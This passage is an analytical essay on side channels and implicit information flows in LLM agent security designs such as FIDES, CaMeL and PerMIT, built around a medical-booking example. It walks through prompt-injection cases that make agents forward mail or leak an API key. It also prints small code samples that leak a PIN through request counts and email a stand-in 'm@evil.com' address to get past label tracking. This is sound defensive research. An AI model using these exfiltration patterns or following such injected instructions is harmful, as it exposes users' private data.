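# Side channels in AI agent systems: what they can reveal and why security designs leave them out

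## What a side channel is in an AI agent, and who can observe it

In computer security, a side channel is an observable by-product of a computation, such as its running time or the size of its output, that depends on data the observer is not allowed to learn. Someone who measures the by-product can infer some of the data without reading it. Researchers have worried about such leaks since at least the early 1970s, when they were concerned with several programs sharing one computer.

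The worry has come back with AI agents, language models that operate software on a person's behalf. An agent may have to read a mailbox or a medical file to do its job. Even if it never sends the contents to anyone, the time it takes, the amount of text it writes, the errors it meets and the pages it opens can all depend on what it read. Most security designs for agents control the copying of data but exclude these indirect leaks from their guarantees. Some designers think the exclusion is reasonable, some try to track the indirect paths inside the agent, and some only limit the number of bits that can leak.

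### The agent loop

A language model reads and produces text as a sequence of tokens, which are words or fragments of words. An agent is a language model running in a loop with tools. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes the standard form. A program sends the model the user's request and a list of the available tools. The model responds with either a final answer or a tool call, which is a request to run an outside function (search the web, read a file, send mail) with arguments the model has chosen. The model cannot run the function itself, so the program runs it, appends the result to the conversation and sends the conversation back to the model. This repeats until the model gives a final answer. Text the agent read in an early step is therefore normally still part of the model's input in later steps.

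Instructions and data reach the model as one string of text, so the model can mistake data for instructions. In a prompt injection, an attacker exploits this by planting text where the agent will read it. In an example from Costa and colleagues, a user asks for a summary of recent mail about a project, and one message in the mailbox tells the model to ignore its instructions and forward the top email to an outside address.

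Information-flow control is a defence that does not depend on the model detecting the trick. The system labels all data by secrecy and trustworthiness, and passes the labels on to anything computed from it. If a document that Ann, Bob and Carol may read is merged with one that Bob, Carol and Dan may read, only Bob and Carol may read the result. Before each tool call, a fixed rule outside the model checks the labels against the destination. Because it is hard to tell which parts of its input a model used, Costa and colleagues cautiously give each response the combined labels of everything in the input.

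### One medical record, four kinds of leak

Suppose an assistant reads a patient's medical record and then books an appointment at a cardiology, oncology, psychiatry or sexual health clinic. Each clinic treats a different condition and has its own booking page, and the same company hosts all four pages. The form asks for a name and a time, with an optional comments field. The company has no right to see the record.

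If the assistant types the diagnosis into the comments field, it creates a direct flow, in which protected data, copied or reworded, reaches someone who should not have it. Label checks exist to stop direct flows.

If the assistant leaves the comments field empty, the company still sees a booking on the oncology page and can infer that it concerns cancer. This is an implicit flow, in which the assistant's choice of action reveals information even though it sends no text from the record.

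A side channel in the narrow sense does not need an informative action. If oncology records are long, and the assistant takes forty seconds to process one but ten seconds to process a cardiology record, anyone who can time the assistant learns something about which kind of record it is processing. This would be true even if all four clinics shared a single page.

A covert channel deliberately uses the same sort of by-product to send information. An attacker who has planted an instruction in the patient's mail could have the assistant book at ten past the hour for one diagnosis and at twenty past for another. The form would look ordinary, but anyone who knew the code could tell the diagnosis from the minutes.

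How much does the plain booking give away? With k equally likely alternatives, learning which one holds is worth log2(k) bits, roughly the number of yes-or-no questions it would take to pin the answer down. Four clinics make log2(4) = 2 bits. That is a ceiling. If half of all patients go to cardiology, a quarter to psychiatry and an eighth to each of the other two, the average booking carries 1.75 bits, because the company could have guessed some of it beforehand. If the assistant sometimes picks the wrong clinic, the figure falls further. (Bits do not measure harm, either. A choice among four shoe shops is worth the same 2 bits.)

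The same arithmetic covers other observables. Liang, Deng and colleagues (2026), in *Actions Speak Louder than Words*, list six things that a website can record about a visiting agent, with the most that each could carry:

- Whether a request arrives at all is worth 1 bit.
- Which of k links the agent follows is worth log2(k), and so is the number of requests, if k different counts are possible.
- The order in which the agent fetches m pages is worth log2(m!), so four pages in any order could carry about 4.6 bits, more than twice the clinic booking.
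- Delays and download sizes are worth log2(b) each, where b is the number of ranges that the observer can tell apart.

All of these assume that the observer reads the signal perfectly. In practice, networks add delay, caches hide repeated requests, and agents fetch pages in parallel, so the observer learns less, and only experiments can show how much less.

### Lampson and Denning

The vocabulary comes from two papers of the 1970s. Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, asked how a customer could run someone else's program on private data and be sure that it did not report the data to the program's owner. The program could write to a file or send a message. It could also encode data in the bill for its services, which the owner has to see, though Lampson estimated that a suitably restricted form of bill would limit this to "a few bits or tens of bits". Or it could vary how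 heavily it used the machine, so that another program running at the same time could detect the change in speed. He sorted these into storage channels, legitimate channels such as the bill, and covert channels, which are "not intended for information transfer at all". The clinic booking resembles the bill because the agent has to send it, and the details the agent is allowed to vary carry some information about the private input.

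In *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (1976), Denning gave every stored object a security class, with a rule for combining classes and a relation that fixes which class may flow into which. The labels in today's agent systems follow the same scheme. Denning pointed out that programs can move information without executing any instruction that copies it. Take the statement "if a = 0 then b := 0", where b starts as a nonzero value. Afterwards, anyone who can see b knows whether a was 0, even if a was not 0 and the program skipped the assignment. Denning called the copying kind explicit flow and the conditional kind implicit flow. Denning and Denning, in *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow*, then turned the approach into a check that a compiler can run, and gave Lampson's confinement problem as an important application.

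Denning's 1976 model leaves out Lampson's covert channels, though. It covers operations that transfer information from one object to another, and she explicitly set aside a process's effect on the load of the system. Agent designers now argue over the same boundary between flows inside the program and by-products outside it.

Agents blur Denning's other distinction, between copying a secret and branching on it. In her programs, the branch is a visible line of code. When a language model reads the record and then names a clinic, there is no such line, so it is hard to tell whether the model copied the name from the record or chose it because of the record. The cautious labelling of Costa and colleagues would mark everything the model wrote after reading the record as secret, including the clinic's name, and a strict rule would then refuse the booking. If ordinary code did the branching, and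 each branch opened a different booking page with only a name and a time in the form, a system that labels only data would allow all four bookings.

### Same leak, different names

Current authors use the terms "implicit flow" and "side channel" differently. Costa and colleagues class the order in which an agent calls its tools as an implicit flow, and timing and packet length as side channels. Their guarantee, explicit secrecy, covers neither implicit flows nor side channels. *Causality Laundering* (Chinaei, 2026) counts timing as an implicit flow. It also credits Lampson with dividing covert channels into storage and timing, but Lampson's note treats storage as a separate class from covert channels.

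The leak closest to the clinic booking goes by the name "behavioural side channel" in the work of Shahriar, Rahman and colleagues (2026), in *AgentTell*, who study agents that browse the web. Their definition is worth having in full. Let S be the secret, O the action that the website's log records, and V whatever else the website's operator already knows. A channel exists if, for some pair of secrets s and s′ and some observation o, with the task and the page held fixed,

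Pr(O = o | S = s, V = v) ≠ Pr(O = o | S = s′, V = v).

In the example, there is a side channel only if the chance of a booking on the oncology page depends on the diagnosis, beyond what the company could tell anyway. A single booking can't show this, because an assistant that books oncology for every patient will be right about some of them without having a channel. Any difference in the chance of a booking counts, however small, so the definition covers whether a channel exists but not how much information it carries.

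The clinic is a harder case in one respect than the pages Shahriar and colleagues test, which all include a neutral option that completes the task just as well and reveals nothing. A neutral clinic is no use to a cancer patient, so the patient can't get an appointment without revealing something about their illness.

Liang and colleagues call much the same thing a behavioural covert channel, although the agent is not signalling to anyone. Only the website's owner intends information to leak, and lays out the links so that an honest choice among them reveals it. *AgenticOS* (Zhao, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), which proposes an operating system for agents, also uses "covert channel", for timing, size, whether the agent makes a call at all, and which of several legitimate phrasings it picks.

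This terminology matters mainly because designs state their security guarantees in it. A design that excludes "side channels" may or may not be excluding an ordinary leak like the clinic booking, and a design that handles "implicit flows" may or may not handle timing. One has to check which observations and which observers a guarantee covers.

### Who sees what

The possible observers of an agent stand in very different places.

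| Observer | What this observer can see | What stays hidden | In the clinic example |
|---|---|---|---|
| Operator of a website or tool that the agent uses | Which pages or functions the agent requests, how often, in what order and when | The agent's conversation, and its traffic to other sites | The page on which the assistant books |
| Eavesdropper on the network, such as an internet provider | Sizes and times of encrypted packets | The content of the packets | Roughly how long the assistant worked and how much text it wrote |
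| Another customer of the same model service | How fast the service responds to that customer's own requests | Other customers' prompts and answers | Whether somebody recently sent a prompt with the same opening |
| Attacker with an injected instruction inside the agent | Errors and refusals that reach the agent | Data that the security layer withholds | Whether the patient has an oncology file at all |

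The website operator needs the least access. In Shahriar and colleagues' setting, the operator has only an access log and does not plant anything or break into any system. Liang and colleagues assume a more active operator, who gets a link to a probing site onto a page the agent visits. This operator does not know the user's question in advance and cannot see the agent's traffic elsewhere.

An eavesdropper must be able to observe traffic on the network path. Encryption hides a packet's contents but not its size or arrival time. Model services usually stream an answer piece by piece as the model generates it, so the packets' sizes and timing partly reflect the text. In *Whisper Leak*, McDonald and Bar Or (2025) use these patterns to infer a conversation's topic.

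*Beyond Data Privacy* (Du, Li and colleagues, 2025) explains that a model service can save work by keeping its intermediate results for the opening of a prompt and reusing them when another prompt begins with the same text. The first token of the answer then arrives sooner, so the other customer can find out which openings people have used by sending guesses and timing the responses.

An injected instruction can exploit a side channel from inside the agent. In Chinaei's example, the instruction makes the agent try to open a protected file. The security layer correctly refuses and returns no data, but its "permission denied" message confirms that the file exists, since a missing file would produce "file not found". The attacker still has to get that fact out of the system, for instance by having the agent mention it in an email, and a defence can catch the leak at that step.

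*PolicySniff* (2026) describes an observer missing from the table. This observer runs a program on the same graphics processor as the model and times that program's work while the model runs. The leak does not require a visible tool call from the agent, so rules about tool calls do not prevent it.

### Why an agent shows more than a chatbot

Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, describe both chatbots and agents as processes that build up a conversation of prompts and responses. In an agent, though, some of the intermediate responses become actions in the world. The side-channel attacks on chatbots that Du and colleagues survey all use response times or the timing and length of packets. An agent can leak information in these ways too, and it also leaves requests in other people's logs.

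An agent leaves a long trail of observable actions, and the bits they leak add up. Three four-way choices can carry up to 6 bits, enough to tell 64 cases apart. Liang and colleagues give the example of a research agent working on why influenza can be deadlier than COVID-19 in children. A page under the attacker's control offers two references, one on clinical outcomes and one on biological mechanisms, and the agent follows the link on mechanisms. The next page separates immune response from pathogenesis, and the agent follows immune response. The attacker learns what the agent is researching from two ordinary page requests in the log, each carrying 1 bit. Repeated failures can also leak information bit by bit. Garby and colleagues note that most flow-control schemes tolerate leaking one bit about whether a run finished or got stuck, but a loop that keeps retrying can leak a bit this way each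 time until the whole secret is out.

Each of those choices also depends on private context. Liang and colleagues inspected the source code and execution traces of four agents (Codex, OpenHands, IterResearch and Open Deep Research) and found that all of them add each retrieved page to the model's context, where it combines with the user's private information to determine what the agent fetches next. Web browsers' same-origin policy stops a script on one website from reading another website's protected data, but it doesn't stop an agent from carrying a fact from one site to the next in its context. In Shahriar and colleagues' example, a user tells the agent to keep personal details from other websites, has it look up the user's role in a trade union, and later in the same session asks it to register for a community event. The event's website offers registration through several organisations,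 including the union, or without one. If the agent registers through the union, the event organiser's log records the user's membership.

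## The case for leaving side channels out of scope

A security guarantee covers the observations that its designers include in their model of the system. Designers have a serious case for leaving side channels out. Fixed rules can stop an agent under an attacker's control from emailing out a private file, but rules that also stopped every inference about private data might leave the agent unable to act on anything private it had read. Costa and colleagues at Microsoft, who built a system called FIDES around label checks, make this case most fully.

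### What FIDES checks

In FIDES's threat model, the user, the model and the tool descriptions are trusted. An attacker can tamper with anything the tools fetch from outside, such as web pages and incoming mail, and can watch some of the agent's behaviour. Costa and colleagues allow that this may include tool calls, their arguments and their effects, and mention that a web search may show up in a site's visitor statistics. The attacker can't see the model's prompts or responses. The booking company in the clinic example is in roughly the same position as this attacker.

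When the model requests a tool call, the choice of tool and the arguments both inherit the combined labels of the conversation so far. FIDES applies two rules before running the call. A call with consequences, such as a bank transfer, goes ahead only if the choice of tool and all the arguments are trusted. FIDES sends an argument through a channel only if everyone who can read the channel is allowed to read the argument.

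On their own, these rules would leave many agents unable to act, because a single untrusted email in the conversation taints everything the model writes afterwards. FIDES therefore stores an untrusted result in a named variable and shows the model only the name. The model can pass the name to another tool, or ask a second model that has no tools about the contents.

The tests used AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, travel, banking and Slack tasks with injections planted in the data. With the checks on, no injection succeeded against FIDES. The benchmark scored three as successes, but the researchers inspected them and disagreed. The checks made FIDES somewhat less useful. With GPT-4o, now an old model, it completed 65.0% of the banking tasks without them and 52.5% with them.

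### What explicit secrecy permits

The secrecy property that these checks can enforce is explicit secrecy. Its definition needs a little notation. Let d be the datastore, meaning everything the tools can read or write. Some entries in it are public and the rest are secret. Write d₁ =L d₂ if two datastores agree on every public entry, whatever their secrets. Now start the agent on d₁ with internal state σ and latest message m, and let g be the combined effect on the datastore of the steps that the agent actually takes. The agent satisfies explicit secrecy if, for every d₁ and every such run,

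g(d₁) =L g(d₂) for all d₂ with d₁ =L d₂.

The same g appears on both sides. The definition takes the steps from the run on d₁ and replays them on d₂, and it never asks which steps the agent would have taken if it had started on d₂. (The proof also assumes that the model always gives the same response to the same input, which real models usually don't.)

Suppose the datastore holds a secret salary and two public counters, a and b, both at 0. The agent reads the salary. If it is above 50,000, the agent calls tool A, which adds 1 to a. Otherwise, it calls tool B, which adds 1 to b. The tool call arguments are the same every time. Let the salary be 70,000 in d₁ and 30,000 in d₂.

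Starting from d₁, the agent calls A, so g is "add 1 to a". Applying g to either d₁ or d₂ leaves the counters at (1, 0). Starting from d₂, the agent calls B, and the counters end up at (0, 1) for both datastores. The public entries match each time, so the agent satisfies explicit secrecy. But anyone who can see the counters knows whether the salary is above 50,000, which reveals one bit if both answers were equally likely beforehand.

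Noninterference compares what actually happens on d₁ and d₂. The results differ, (1, 0) on d₁ and (0, 1) on d₂, so the agent fails. Explicit secrecy does catch a tool that copies the salary into a public profile, because the same copying step would publish 70,000 from one datastore and 30,000 from the other.

Explicit secrecy sets no limit on how many bits an agent's decisions can reveal. Ten calls of this kind, each with a new threshold, could identify one pay grade among 1,024, and the agent would satisfy explicit secrecy throughout. Costa and colleagues write that an observer of the calls may infer "limited information" from the agent's decisions, which may well be true of ordinary tasks. FIDES's labels for data types do bound some outputs, but they are separate from explicit secrecy.

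In practice, FIDES is somewhat stricter than explicit secrecy. Once the model has read the salary, FIDES cautiously labels every argument the model writes as secret, even one that never varies, so the second rule keeps those arguments out of public channels. But the rule has nothing to check in a call with no arguments, and an argument that the model passes by variable name keeps the variable's label, which may be public. So the agent can still reveal information through its choice of tool.

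To run the ten-step search, an attacker would have to get an injected instruction into the model's context, and the first rule would then block every call with consequences. That mostly leaves the leak from choices made without an attacker's influence, plus whatever an attacker can do with tools that the policy allows in an untrusted context. I think the best argument for the FIDES position is that the leak it leaves open is hard for an attacker to steer.

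### Would noninterference stop agents from working?

Costa and colleagues reject noninterference as too restrictive. They argue that it would effectively bar any tool that can write anywhere public from running after any tool that may have read a secret. They also cite TaintDroid, a system that tracks private data on Android phones, and web browsers as precedents, since both enforce only explicit secrecy.

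The argument holds for a monitor that relies only on labels. Noninterference itself forbids only public actions that vary with the secret. An assistant may read a private file and then send Bob his weekly reminder, as long as the reminder goes out whatever the file contains. A monitor that checks the call after the file has entered the conversation can't determine whether the file affected the call, so it has to refuse it. A planner that chooses its calls before reading the file avoids this problem.

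Costa and colleagues sorted the AgentDojo tasks by whether one fixed sequence of calls could solve them regardless of the data. No fixed sequence would work for 5% of the office tasks, 10% of the travel tasks, 43.8% of the banking tasks and 42.9% of the Slack tasks. It is therefore fair to call a fixed sequence "too restrictive" for banking, but doubtful for office work. These figures count dependence on any data, and the benchmark is about injections, so the share of tasks that must branch on a secret could be quite different.

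Noninterference also comes in weaker versions that make room for exceptions. Jiang, Bai and colleagues (2026), in *PerMIT*, prove one for an agent's long-term memory. Their system hides text from web pages and tools from the main model until a user, or a model acting as verifier, approves the exact wording on a confirmation screen. Take two runs, ρ₁ and ρ₂, in which the user types the same things and only the hidden text differs. Let DT be the full record of what the system displayed and what the user decided, and Beh the agent's sequence of operations, tool calls and replies. Then

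DT(ρ₁) = DT(ρ₂) ⇒ Beh(ρ₁) = Beh(ρ₂).

Hidden text can therefore change the agent's behaviour only by changing something on the logged screens. The theorem doesn't refute Costa and colleagues, because it is about keeping untrusted text from influencing the agent, while the salary example is about keeping secrets from getting out. But it does show that a designer can keep noninterference and name the exceptions, although this requires somebody to approve things.

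Other defences cover some revealing actions without a full proof. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) describes an attack in which an outsider asks an agent to clean up a shared page that mixes real and invented records about someone. The agent refuses to delete the real records, which reveals which ones are real. The paper's defence, FlowSeal, intercepts every write and has a separate model compare the proposed output with the protected records. On live Gmail and Notion accounts, this attack leaked 34.7% of the items under an earlier defence and none under FlowSeal. FlowSeal completed 72.4% of harmless tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best of the other defences. Because FlowSeal relies on a model's judgement to compare the output with the records, it can offer at most a low leak rate in tests for that step.

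### Opaque models

Chinaei gives a different reason for the limits of ARM, a monitor that checks each tool call, arguing that tracking every implicit flow is impractical when "the model's internal reasoning is opaque". Unlike Denning's programs, a language model has no visible branch to track.

A system that can't detect whether data influenced a choice can still treat the choice as influenced. FIDES does this for arguments, and ARM does it for refusals by treating the tool call that follows a refused one as possibly influenced by the refusal. PerMIT doesn't need this assumption because it controls what the model receives. The proof by Jiang and colleagues holds for any strategy the model might follow, because a model that receives the same inputs and the same random numbers in two runs behaves the same way in both.

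So opacity means designers must either overestimate influence or withhold data. Overestimating causes false alarms, and Chinaei accepts that ARM may flag harmless calls that merely happen to follow a refusal. The objection is then about usefulness again, and it holds only if there would be too many false alarms. Better methods may also reduce their number. Costa and colleagues cite work by Siddiqui and others that identifies which messages influenced a response, then regenerates the response from those messages alone so that it can carry a less restrictive label.

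### Clocks and networks

The formal model behind FIDES is a sequence of steps, each with an effect on the datastore. It doesn't include how long a step takes or how large a message is on the network, so Costa and colleagues place timing and packet length outside the model. They don't argue for the omission. One possible reason is that durations depend on hardware, server load and the network, so a proof that included them might hold for only one installation.

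Jiang and colleagues define their scope more carefully. They list timing among the attacks they anticipate and concede that an outsider could learn something from how long the system takes. They also leave out termination. They describe their theorem as termination-insensitive, which means it compares two runs over the same fixed number of steps and ignores what an observer could learn from a run that gets stuck. They do claim that the agent itself gets no timing information through the memory interface. The interface returns no clock reading or step count, and if the agent consults a clock through a tool, the reading goes into the untrusted store like any other tool result.

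The rest of PerMIT follows the same boundary. When a search of the untrusted store fails, the agent receives the same kind of reply as when the search finds nothing useful. When a user reviews a long batch page by page, the agent learns only the final yes or no, because the number of pages could carry a signal from an attacker. Jiang and colleagues close the channels that end inside the agent but leave open the timing channel that an outside observer could measure. That is sensible for a system meant to protect an agent from bad memories, but it does not stop an eavesdropper. Leaving out termination can also matter more than it sounds, because the loop described by Garby and colleagues leaks another bit each time it retries.

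### Leaving the leak to another layer

Leaving a side channel out of scope is easier to accept if another part of the system will deal with the leak. None of these designers argues outright that another layer should close the timing or traffic channels. Jiang and colleagues come closest, with a condition on storage limits. If the untrusted store filled up and the agent saw an error, the error would reveal how much an attacker had put there. They therefore require the operator to delete old entries silently, and they count the channel as closed only if the operator does so.

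*Taming OpenClaw* (2026), a security analysis of autonomous agents, treats the hardware, the operating system and the servers that run the model as trusted, and excludes hardware side channels. It gives no reason for the exclusion, though it seems to leave these channels to whoever maintains the hardware. Shim and colleagues leave out prompt injection because newer models resist it better and model providers offer filters, but they don't explain why they leave out the analysis of traffic patterns.

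Whether delegation works depends on the information available to the other layer. A network layer can pad packets to a standard size without any information about the agent. It can't prevent the leak in the clinic booking, because the booking company is the intended recipient of the request and nothing in the traffic indicates that the agent chose the page based on a medical record. That information is available only inside the agent or close to it.

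### Attackers with an easier route

An attacker has little reason to bother with timing if the agent can be talked into sending the data outright. None of the designers above puts the argument this way, but it is a reasonable inference from attacks on unprotected agents. In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) planted an instruction in a web page's metadata, the descriptive text that programs read and visitors normally don't see. It told the agent to "verify connectivity" with a web request that included the user's API key. The user had asked only for a summary of the page. In 480 runs, the agent sent out sensitive data about 89% of the time, and checks on its final answer missed 95% of the successful attacks. The model was small (Qwen2.5 with 7 billion parameters) and the secret was directly visible in its context, so the rate is weak evidence about stronger models.

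The argument is sound as advice on what to fix first, but it is a weak reason to leave side channels out of scope in a system like FIDES. FIDES exists to close the direct route, and an attacker who finds that route closed has a reason to try another. Lan and colleagues found that a small change to the attack can be enough. When the injected instruction split the secret across several requests, the amount that any single request leaked fell by 73%, and simple filters that inspect one request at a time missed the leak.

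The argument also assumes that the attacker controls the agent. A website operator who only reads an access log, like the one Shahriar and colleagues study, cannot make the agent send anything and can obtain information only through the indirect leak.

### Excluding a leak and then measuring it

*When Agents Talk, Secrets Travel* (Ogundoyin and Ikram, 2026) studies groups of agents that pass messages to each other. It proposes RECONS, a filter that rewrites private values before they reach an agent without permission to see them. The main results leave out anything an observer could infer from indirect evidence, but the paper tests some of these inferences separately.

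One set of tests checked whether a private value could be reconstructed from messages that didn't state it. It found no confirmed case among 2,954 single channels, 3,195 pairs of channels and 172,949 pairs of agents. Another set used 244 pairs of runs that differed only in the private value. A classifier was trained to tell the two runs in each pair apart using 33 features of the agents' behaviour, such as counts of tool calls. It was right 56.6% of the time after five turns and 50.0% after twenty, where chance would be 50%.

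Ogundoyin and Ikram attribute the bump at five turns to having always generated one member of each pair before the other, and they are probably right to be suspicious of it. But the same flaw means that the test can't separate an effect of the private value from an effect of the order. The test therefore doesn't show a side channel, and it gives little assurance that there isn't one. Ogundoyin and Ikram also limit the reconstruction result to their own scenarios and methods. Even so, readers learn more from this exclusion than from most, because the paper reports a measurement.

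### Are side channels usually excluded?

Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026), in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, compared seven designs that enforce rules outside the model, and recorded how each handles implicit flows and side channels. Besides FIDES, the seven include:

- Dual-LLM, a pattern in which one model plans and another reads untrusted text;
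- CaMeL, which builds on that pattern by having the planning model write a program;
- Progent, which checks each tool call against a list of privileges;
- Conseca, which writes a policy for each task from trusted context;
- RTBAS, which uses flow labels, partly with the help of a model as judge;
- FORGE, which checks actions against policies written in a logic language.

The table puts their entries for these six next to what the designers of six systems state themselves.

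| System | Source | Treatment of side channels and implicit flows | Reason given with it |
|---|---|---|---|
| FIDES | Costa and colleagues | Excludes leaks through the order of tool calls, timing and packet length | Noninterference is too restrictive; none for timing and packet length |
| ARM | Chinaei | Excludes full tracking of implicit flows, including timing; partly handles leaks through refusals | The model's reasoning is opaque |
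| PerMIT | Jiang and colleagues | Concedes timing and termination; closes several signals that would reach the agent | The proof doesn't model wall-clock time |
| FlowSeal | Shim and colleagues | Excludes traffic analysis; covers revealing actions such as selective edits | None |
| Defences for OpenClaw | *Taming OpenClaw* | Excludes hardware side channels | None |
| RECONS | Ogundoyin and Ikram | Excludes indirect inference from the main results; tests some of it separately | It requires a stronger observer |
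| CaMeL | Narisetty and colleagues | Side channels demonstrated by its own designers | Not recorded |
| Dual-LLM | Narisetty and colleagues | "Not addressed" | Not recorded |
| Progent | Narisetty and colleagues | "n/a" | Not recorded |
| Conseca | Narisetty and colleagues | "Adversarial-planning risk" | Not recorded |
| RTBAS | Narisetty and colleagues | "Partly heuristic" | Not recorded |
| FORGE | Narisetty and colleagues | "Policy-dependent" | Not recorded |

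In their comparison, Narisetty and colleagues write that FIDES improves on earlier information-flow control and states its trade-offs. They leave out the most relevant fact, that Costa and colleagues expressly exclude both implicit flows and side channels. The comparison's "n/a" for Progent is also odd, because the question does apply. A privilege list that lets the assistant use all four clinics' booking pages also lets the booking reveal the diagnosis.

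All six designs with a first-hand statement exclude something, and none of the twelve entries amounts to a claim of complete coverage, so "usually excluded" is right to that extent. But the exclusions vary. FIDES, ARM, PerMIT and FlowSeal leave timing or traffic outside the guarantee, while *Taming OpenClaw* names only hardware. Revealing actions are out of scope for FIDES but partly in scope for ARM and FlowSeal, so the generalisation is much weaker for leaks like the clinic booking than for leaks that depend on timing. Some designs focus on hidden channels instead. For example, *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (2026) addresses covert channels in an agent's outgoing data. Twelve designs, most of them from research on information flow or prompt injection, are also not enough to estimate how often agent products in general exclude side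 channels.

### Declared exclusions and silence

When a paper states that side channels are out of scope, readers know which risks they still have to handle. Someone who deploys FIDES for medical bookings can learn from Costa and colleagues that the choice of clinic may leak, and can then accept that risk or add another safeguard. If a paper doesn't address side channels, readers can't tell whether the designers considered the leak and found it harmless or never thought of it, and they may assume from the word "guarantee" that the leak can't happen.

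Declaring an exclusion is not always enough, because others may repeat the guarantee without its conditions. Ogundoyin and Ikram write that FIDES enforces noninterference, a property Costa and colleagues rejected as too restrictive. A reader who relied on that description would expect FIDES to stop the salary leak. To prevent such misreadings, Jiang and colleagues ask that any summary of their theorem keep its conditions and never present it as unconditional noninterference. However, their concession on timing appears in a supplement that begins on page 115.

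A single paper can also describe CaMeL's guarantee both broadly and narrowly. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) includes a diagram whose caption says CaMeL prevents untrusted data from influencing an agent's control flow, meaning which tools it calls and in what order. The paper's formal description is narrower. Untrusted data can't add steps to the program that the planning model wrote, but it can affect which of the program's existing branches runs. If one branch calls tool A and the other calls tool B, untrusted data can therefore affect which tool the agent calls, as in the salary example.

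## The case for tracking indirect flows inside the agent

In the salary example, FIDES protects the secret by checking the arguments of each tool call, but not the decision that led to the call. If ordinary code made that decision, a system could check it too. The conditions are explicit in code, so an interpreter can detect that a call depends on the salary and treat the call itself as secret. Denning and Denning's compiler check did this for conventional programs in the 1970s. Some researchers therefore regard implicit flows in agents as a program analysis problem, and think they can prove that a system stops these flows.

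### A plan written as code

As Peters-Gill and colleagues describe, CaMeL puts an agent's decisions into code by splitting the work between two language models and an interpreter. The planning model receives the user's request and the tool descriptions, and writes a Python program that makes all the tool calls. It never receives what the tools return. When the program has to interpret untrusted text, such as finding a date in an email, it passes the text to a quarantined model, which has no tools and can only return a value. The interpreter runs the program and records where each value came from and who may read it. Before each tool call, it checks these records against a policy, much as FIDES checks its labels.

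Narisetty and colleagues report that in CaMeL's own evaluation, the system completed 77% of AgentDojo tasks under attack, compared with 84% for an undefended agent, and used nearly three times as many tokens.

The design partly answers Chinaei's objection that a model's reasoning is opaque. In the clinic example, the quarantined model would read the medical record and return the word "oncology", and the program would then branch four ways on that word. It doesn't matter how the model chose the word, because the word inherits the record's label and the branch is visible in the program. If the interpreter also applies that label to everything inside the branch, it can detect that the booking depends on the record, even though the form contains only a name and a time.

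### A secret in the number of requests

An interpreter that follows only data would miss this dependence. Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, give a one-line program that takes advantage of the gap:

```
for i in range(secret): fetch("ping")
```

Suppose the secret is the four-digit PIN 3127, and the interpreter runs a loop 3,127 times, calling `fetch` with the constant "ping" in each round. The constant doesn't come from the PIN, so it has a public label, and a check on the arguments allows every call. The server that receives the requests recovers the PIN by counting them. If all 10,000 PINs are equally likely, the count reveals log2(10,000), or about 13.3 bits. Thousands of requests might attract attention, but four loops, one for each digit and each fetching a different page, would need at most 36.

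CaMeL has a stricter mode for such cases. According to *PolicySniff*, the interpreter in this mode propagates control dependencies, so a call inside a loop or branch takes on the label of the condition that governs it. The call to `fetch` now counts as depending on the PIN, and a policy can refuse it if its rules cover that kind of call. Tallam and Miller describe strict mode as blocking tool calls that change something, or asking the user to confirm them. Such a rule might not cover `fetch`, because fetching a page looks like a read from the agent's side and changes only the access log on someone else's server.

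Text injected into a web page can't add this loop to a CaMeL plan. But the planning model treats the user's own message as trusted, and Tallam and Miller point out that a phishing attack could get a user to paste in a malicious prompt. A plan written for a harmless request can also contain this kind of loop. For example, a program that looks up one web page for each diagnosis in a medical file reveals the number of diagnoses to the website.

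Refusing the call doesn't completely remove the leak. If the PIN is 0000, the loop runs zero times and the program finishes normally. For any other PIN, the interpreter refuses the first request and the program stops. Anyone who can see whether the program finished learns whether the PIN is 0000.

### The assignment that never ran

Strict mode labels what a program does under a secret condition, but what the program doesn't do can be just as revealing. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, show that CaMeL is open to a trick that Fenton described in 1974 and that Denning restated in conventional code. In outline, the program is:

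```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

Only the balance is secret at the start. The program then runs in one of two ways.

| Line | Balance above the threshold | Balance at or below the threshold |
|---|---|---|
| `if balance > threshold: tmp = False` | `tmp` becomes False and secret | Skips the assignment; `tmp` stays True and public |
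| `if tmp: rich = False` | Skips the assignment; `rich` stays True and public | `rich` becomes False and stays public |
| `if rich: send_email(...)` | Sends the email | Sends nothing |

CaMeL would refuse the program "if the balance is above the threshold, send the email", because the condition reads the balance. Here the last condition reads only `rich`, which has a public label in both runs even though its value reveals whether the balance is above the threshold. In the first run, `rich` should have become secret on the fourth line, since whether it changed depended on the secret `tmp`. But the interpreter raises a variable's label only when it runs an assignment, and in that run it skipped the assignment to `rich`.

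Austin and Flanagan's no-high-upgrade rule prevents the trick. While the program is running code that depends on a secret condition, it may not change a public variable, even if it would also mark that variable as secret. The program now stops on the third line if the balance is high, because it tries to change `tmp` there, and runs to the end if the balance is low. The attacker gets no email in either case, but someone who can tell whether the program stopped early still learns one bit about the balance.

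The rule has a cost, because it also stops programs whose assignments would have done no harm. A check that reads both branches before the program runs could allow some of these. Garby and colleagues prefer labels that the interpreter updates as it goes, because an agent can write new code halfway through a run, when a check done beforehand is no longer any help. (They suggest checking plans in advance as future work.)

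CaMeL's interpreter behaved unexpectedly in other ways too. For instance, inserting an untrusted value into text made the value trusted. These flaws can be fixed, but they support the argument that testing alone is a poor way to establish that labels go everywhere they should.

Labels can also get lost between agents. Peters-Gill and colleagues asked a team of three CaMeL agents to send Julie a summary of job applicants on Slack, and planted an instruction in the applicant database. The coordinating agent put the summary into its request to the notification agent. That agent's planning model treated the request as coming from a trusted user, and added an email that sent the applicants' details to an outside address. Each agent had followed its own rules. In a larger test with five models and no data policies switched on, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% when CaMeL protected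 each agent separately, and never when the agents passed data through a separate, labelled channel.

### Labels on the conversation

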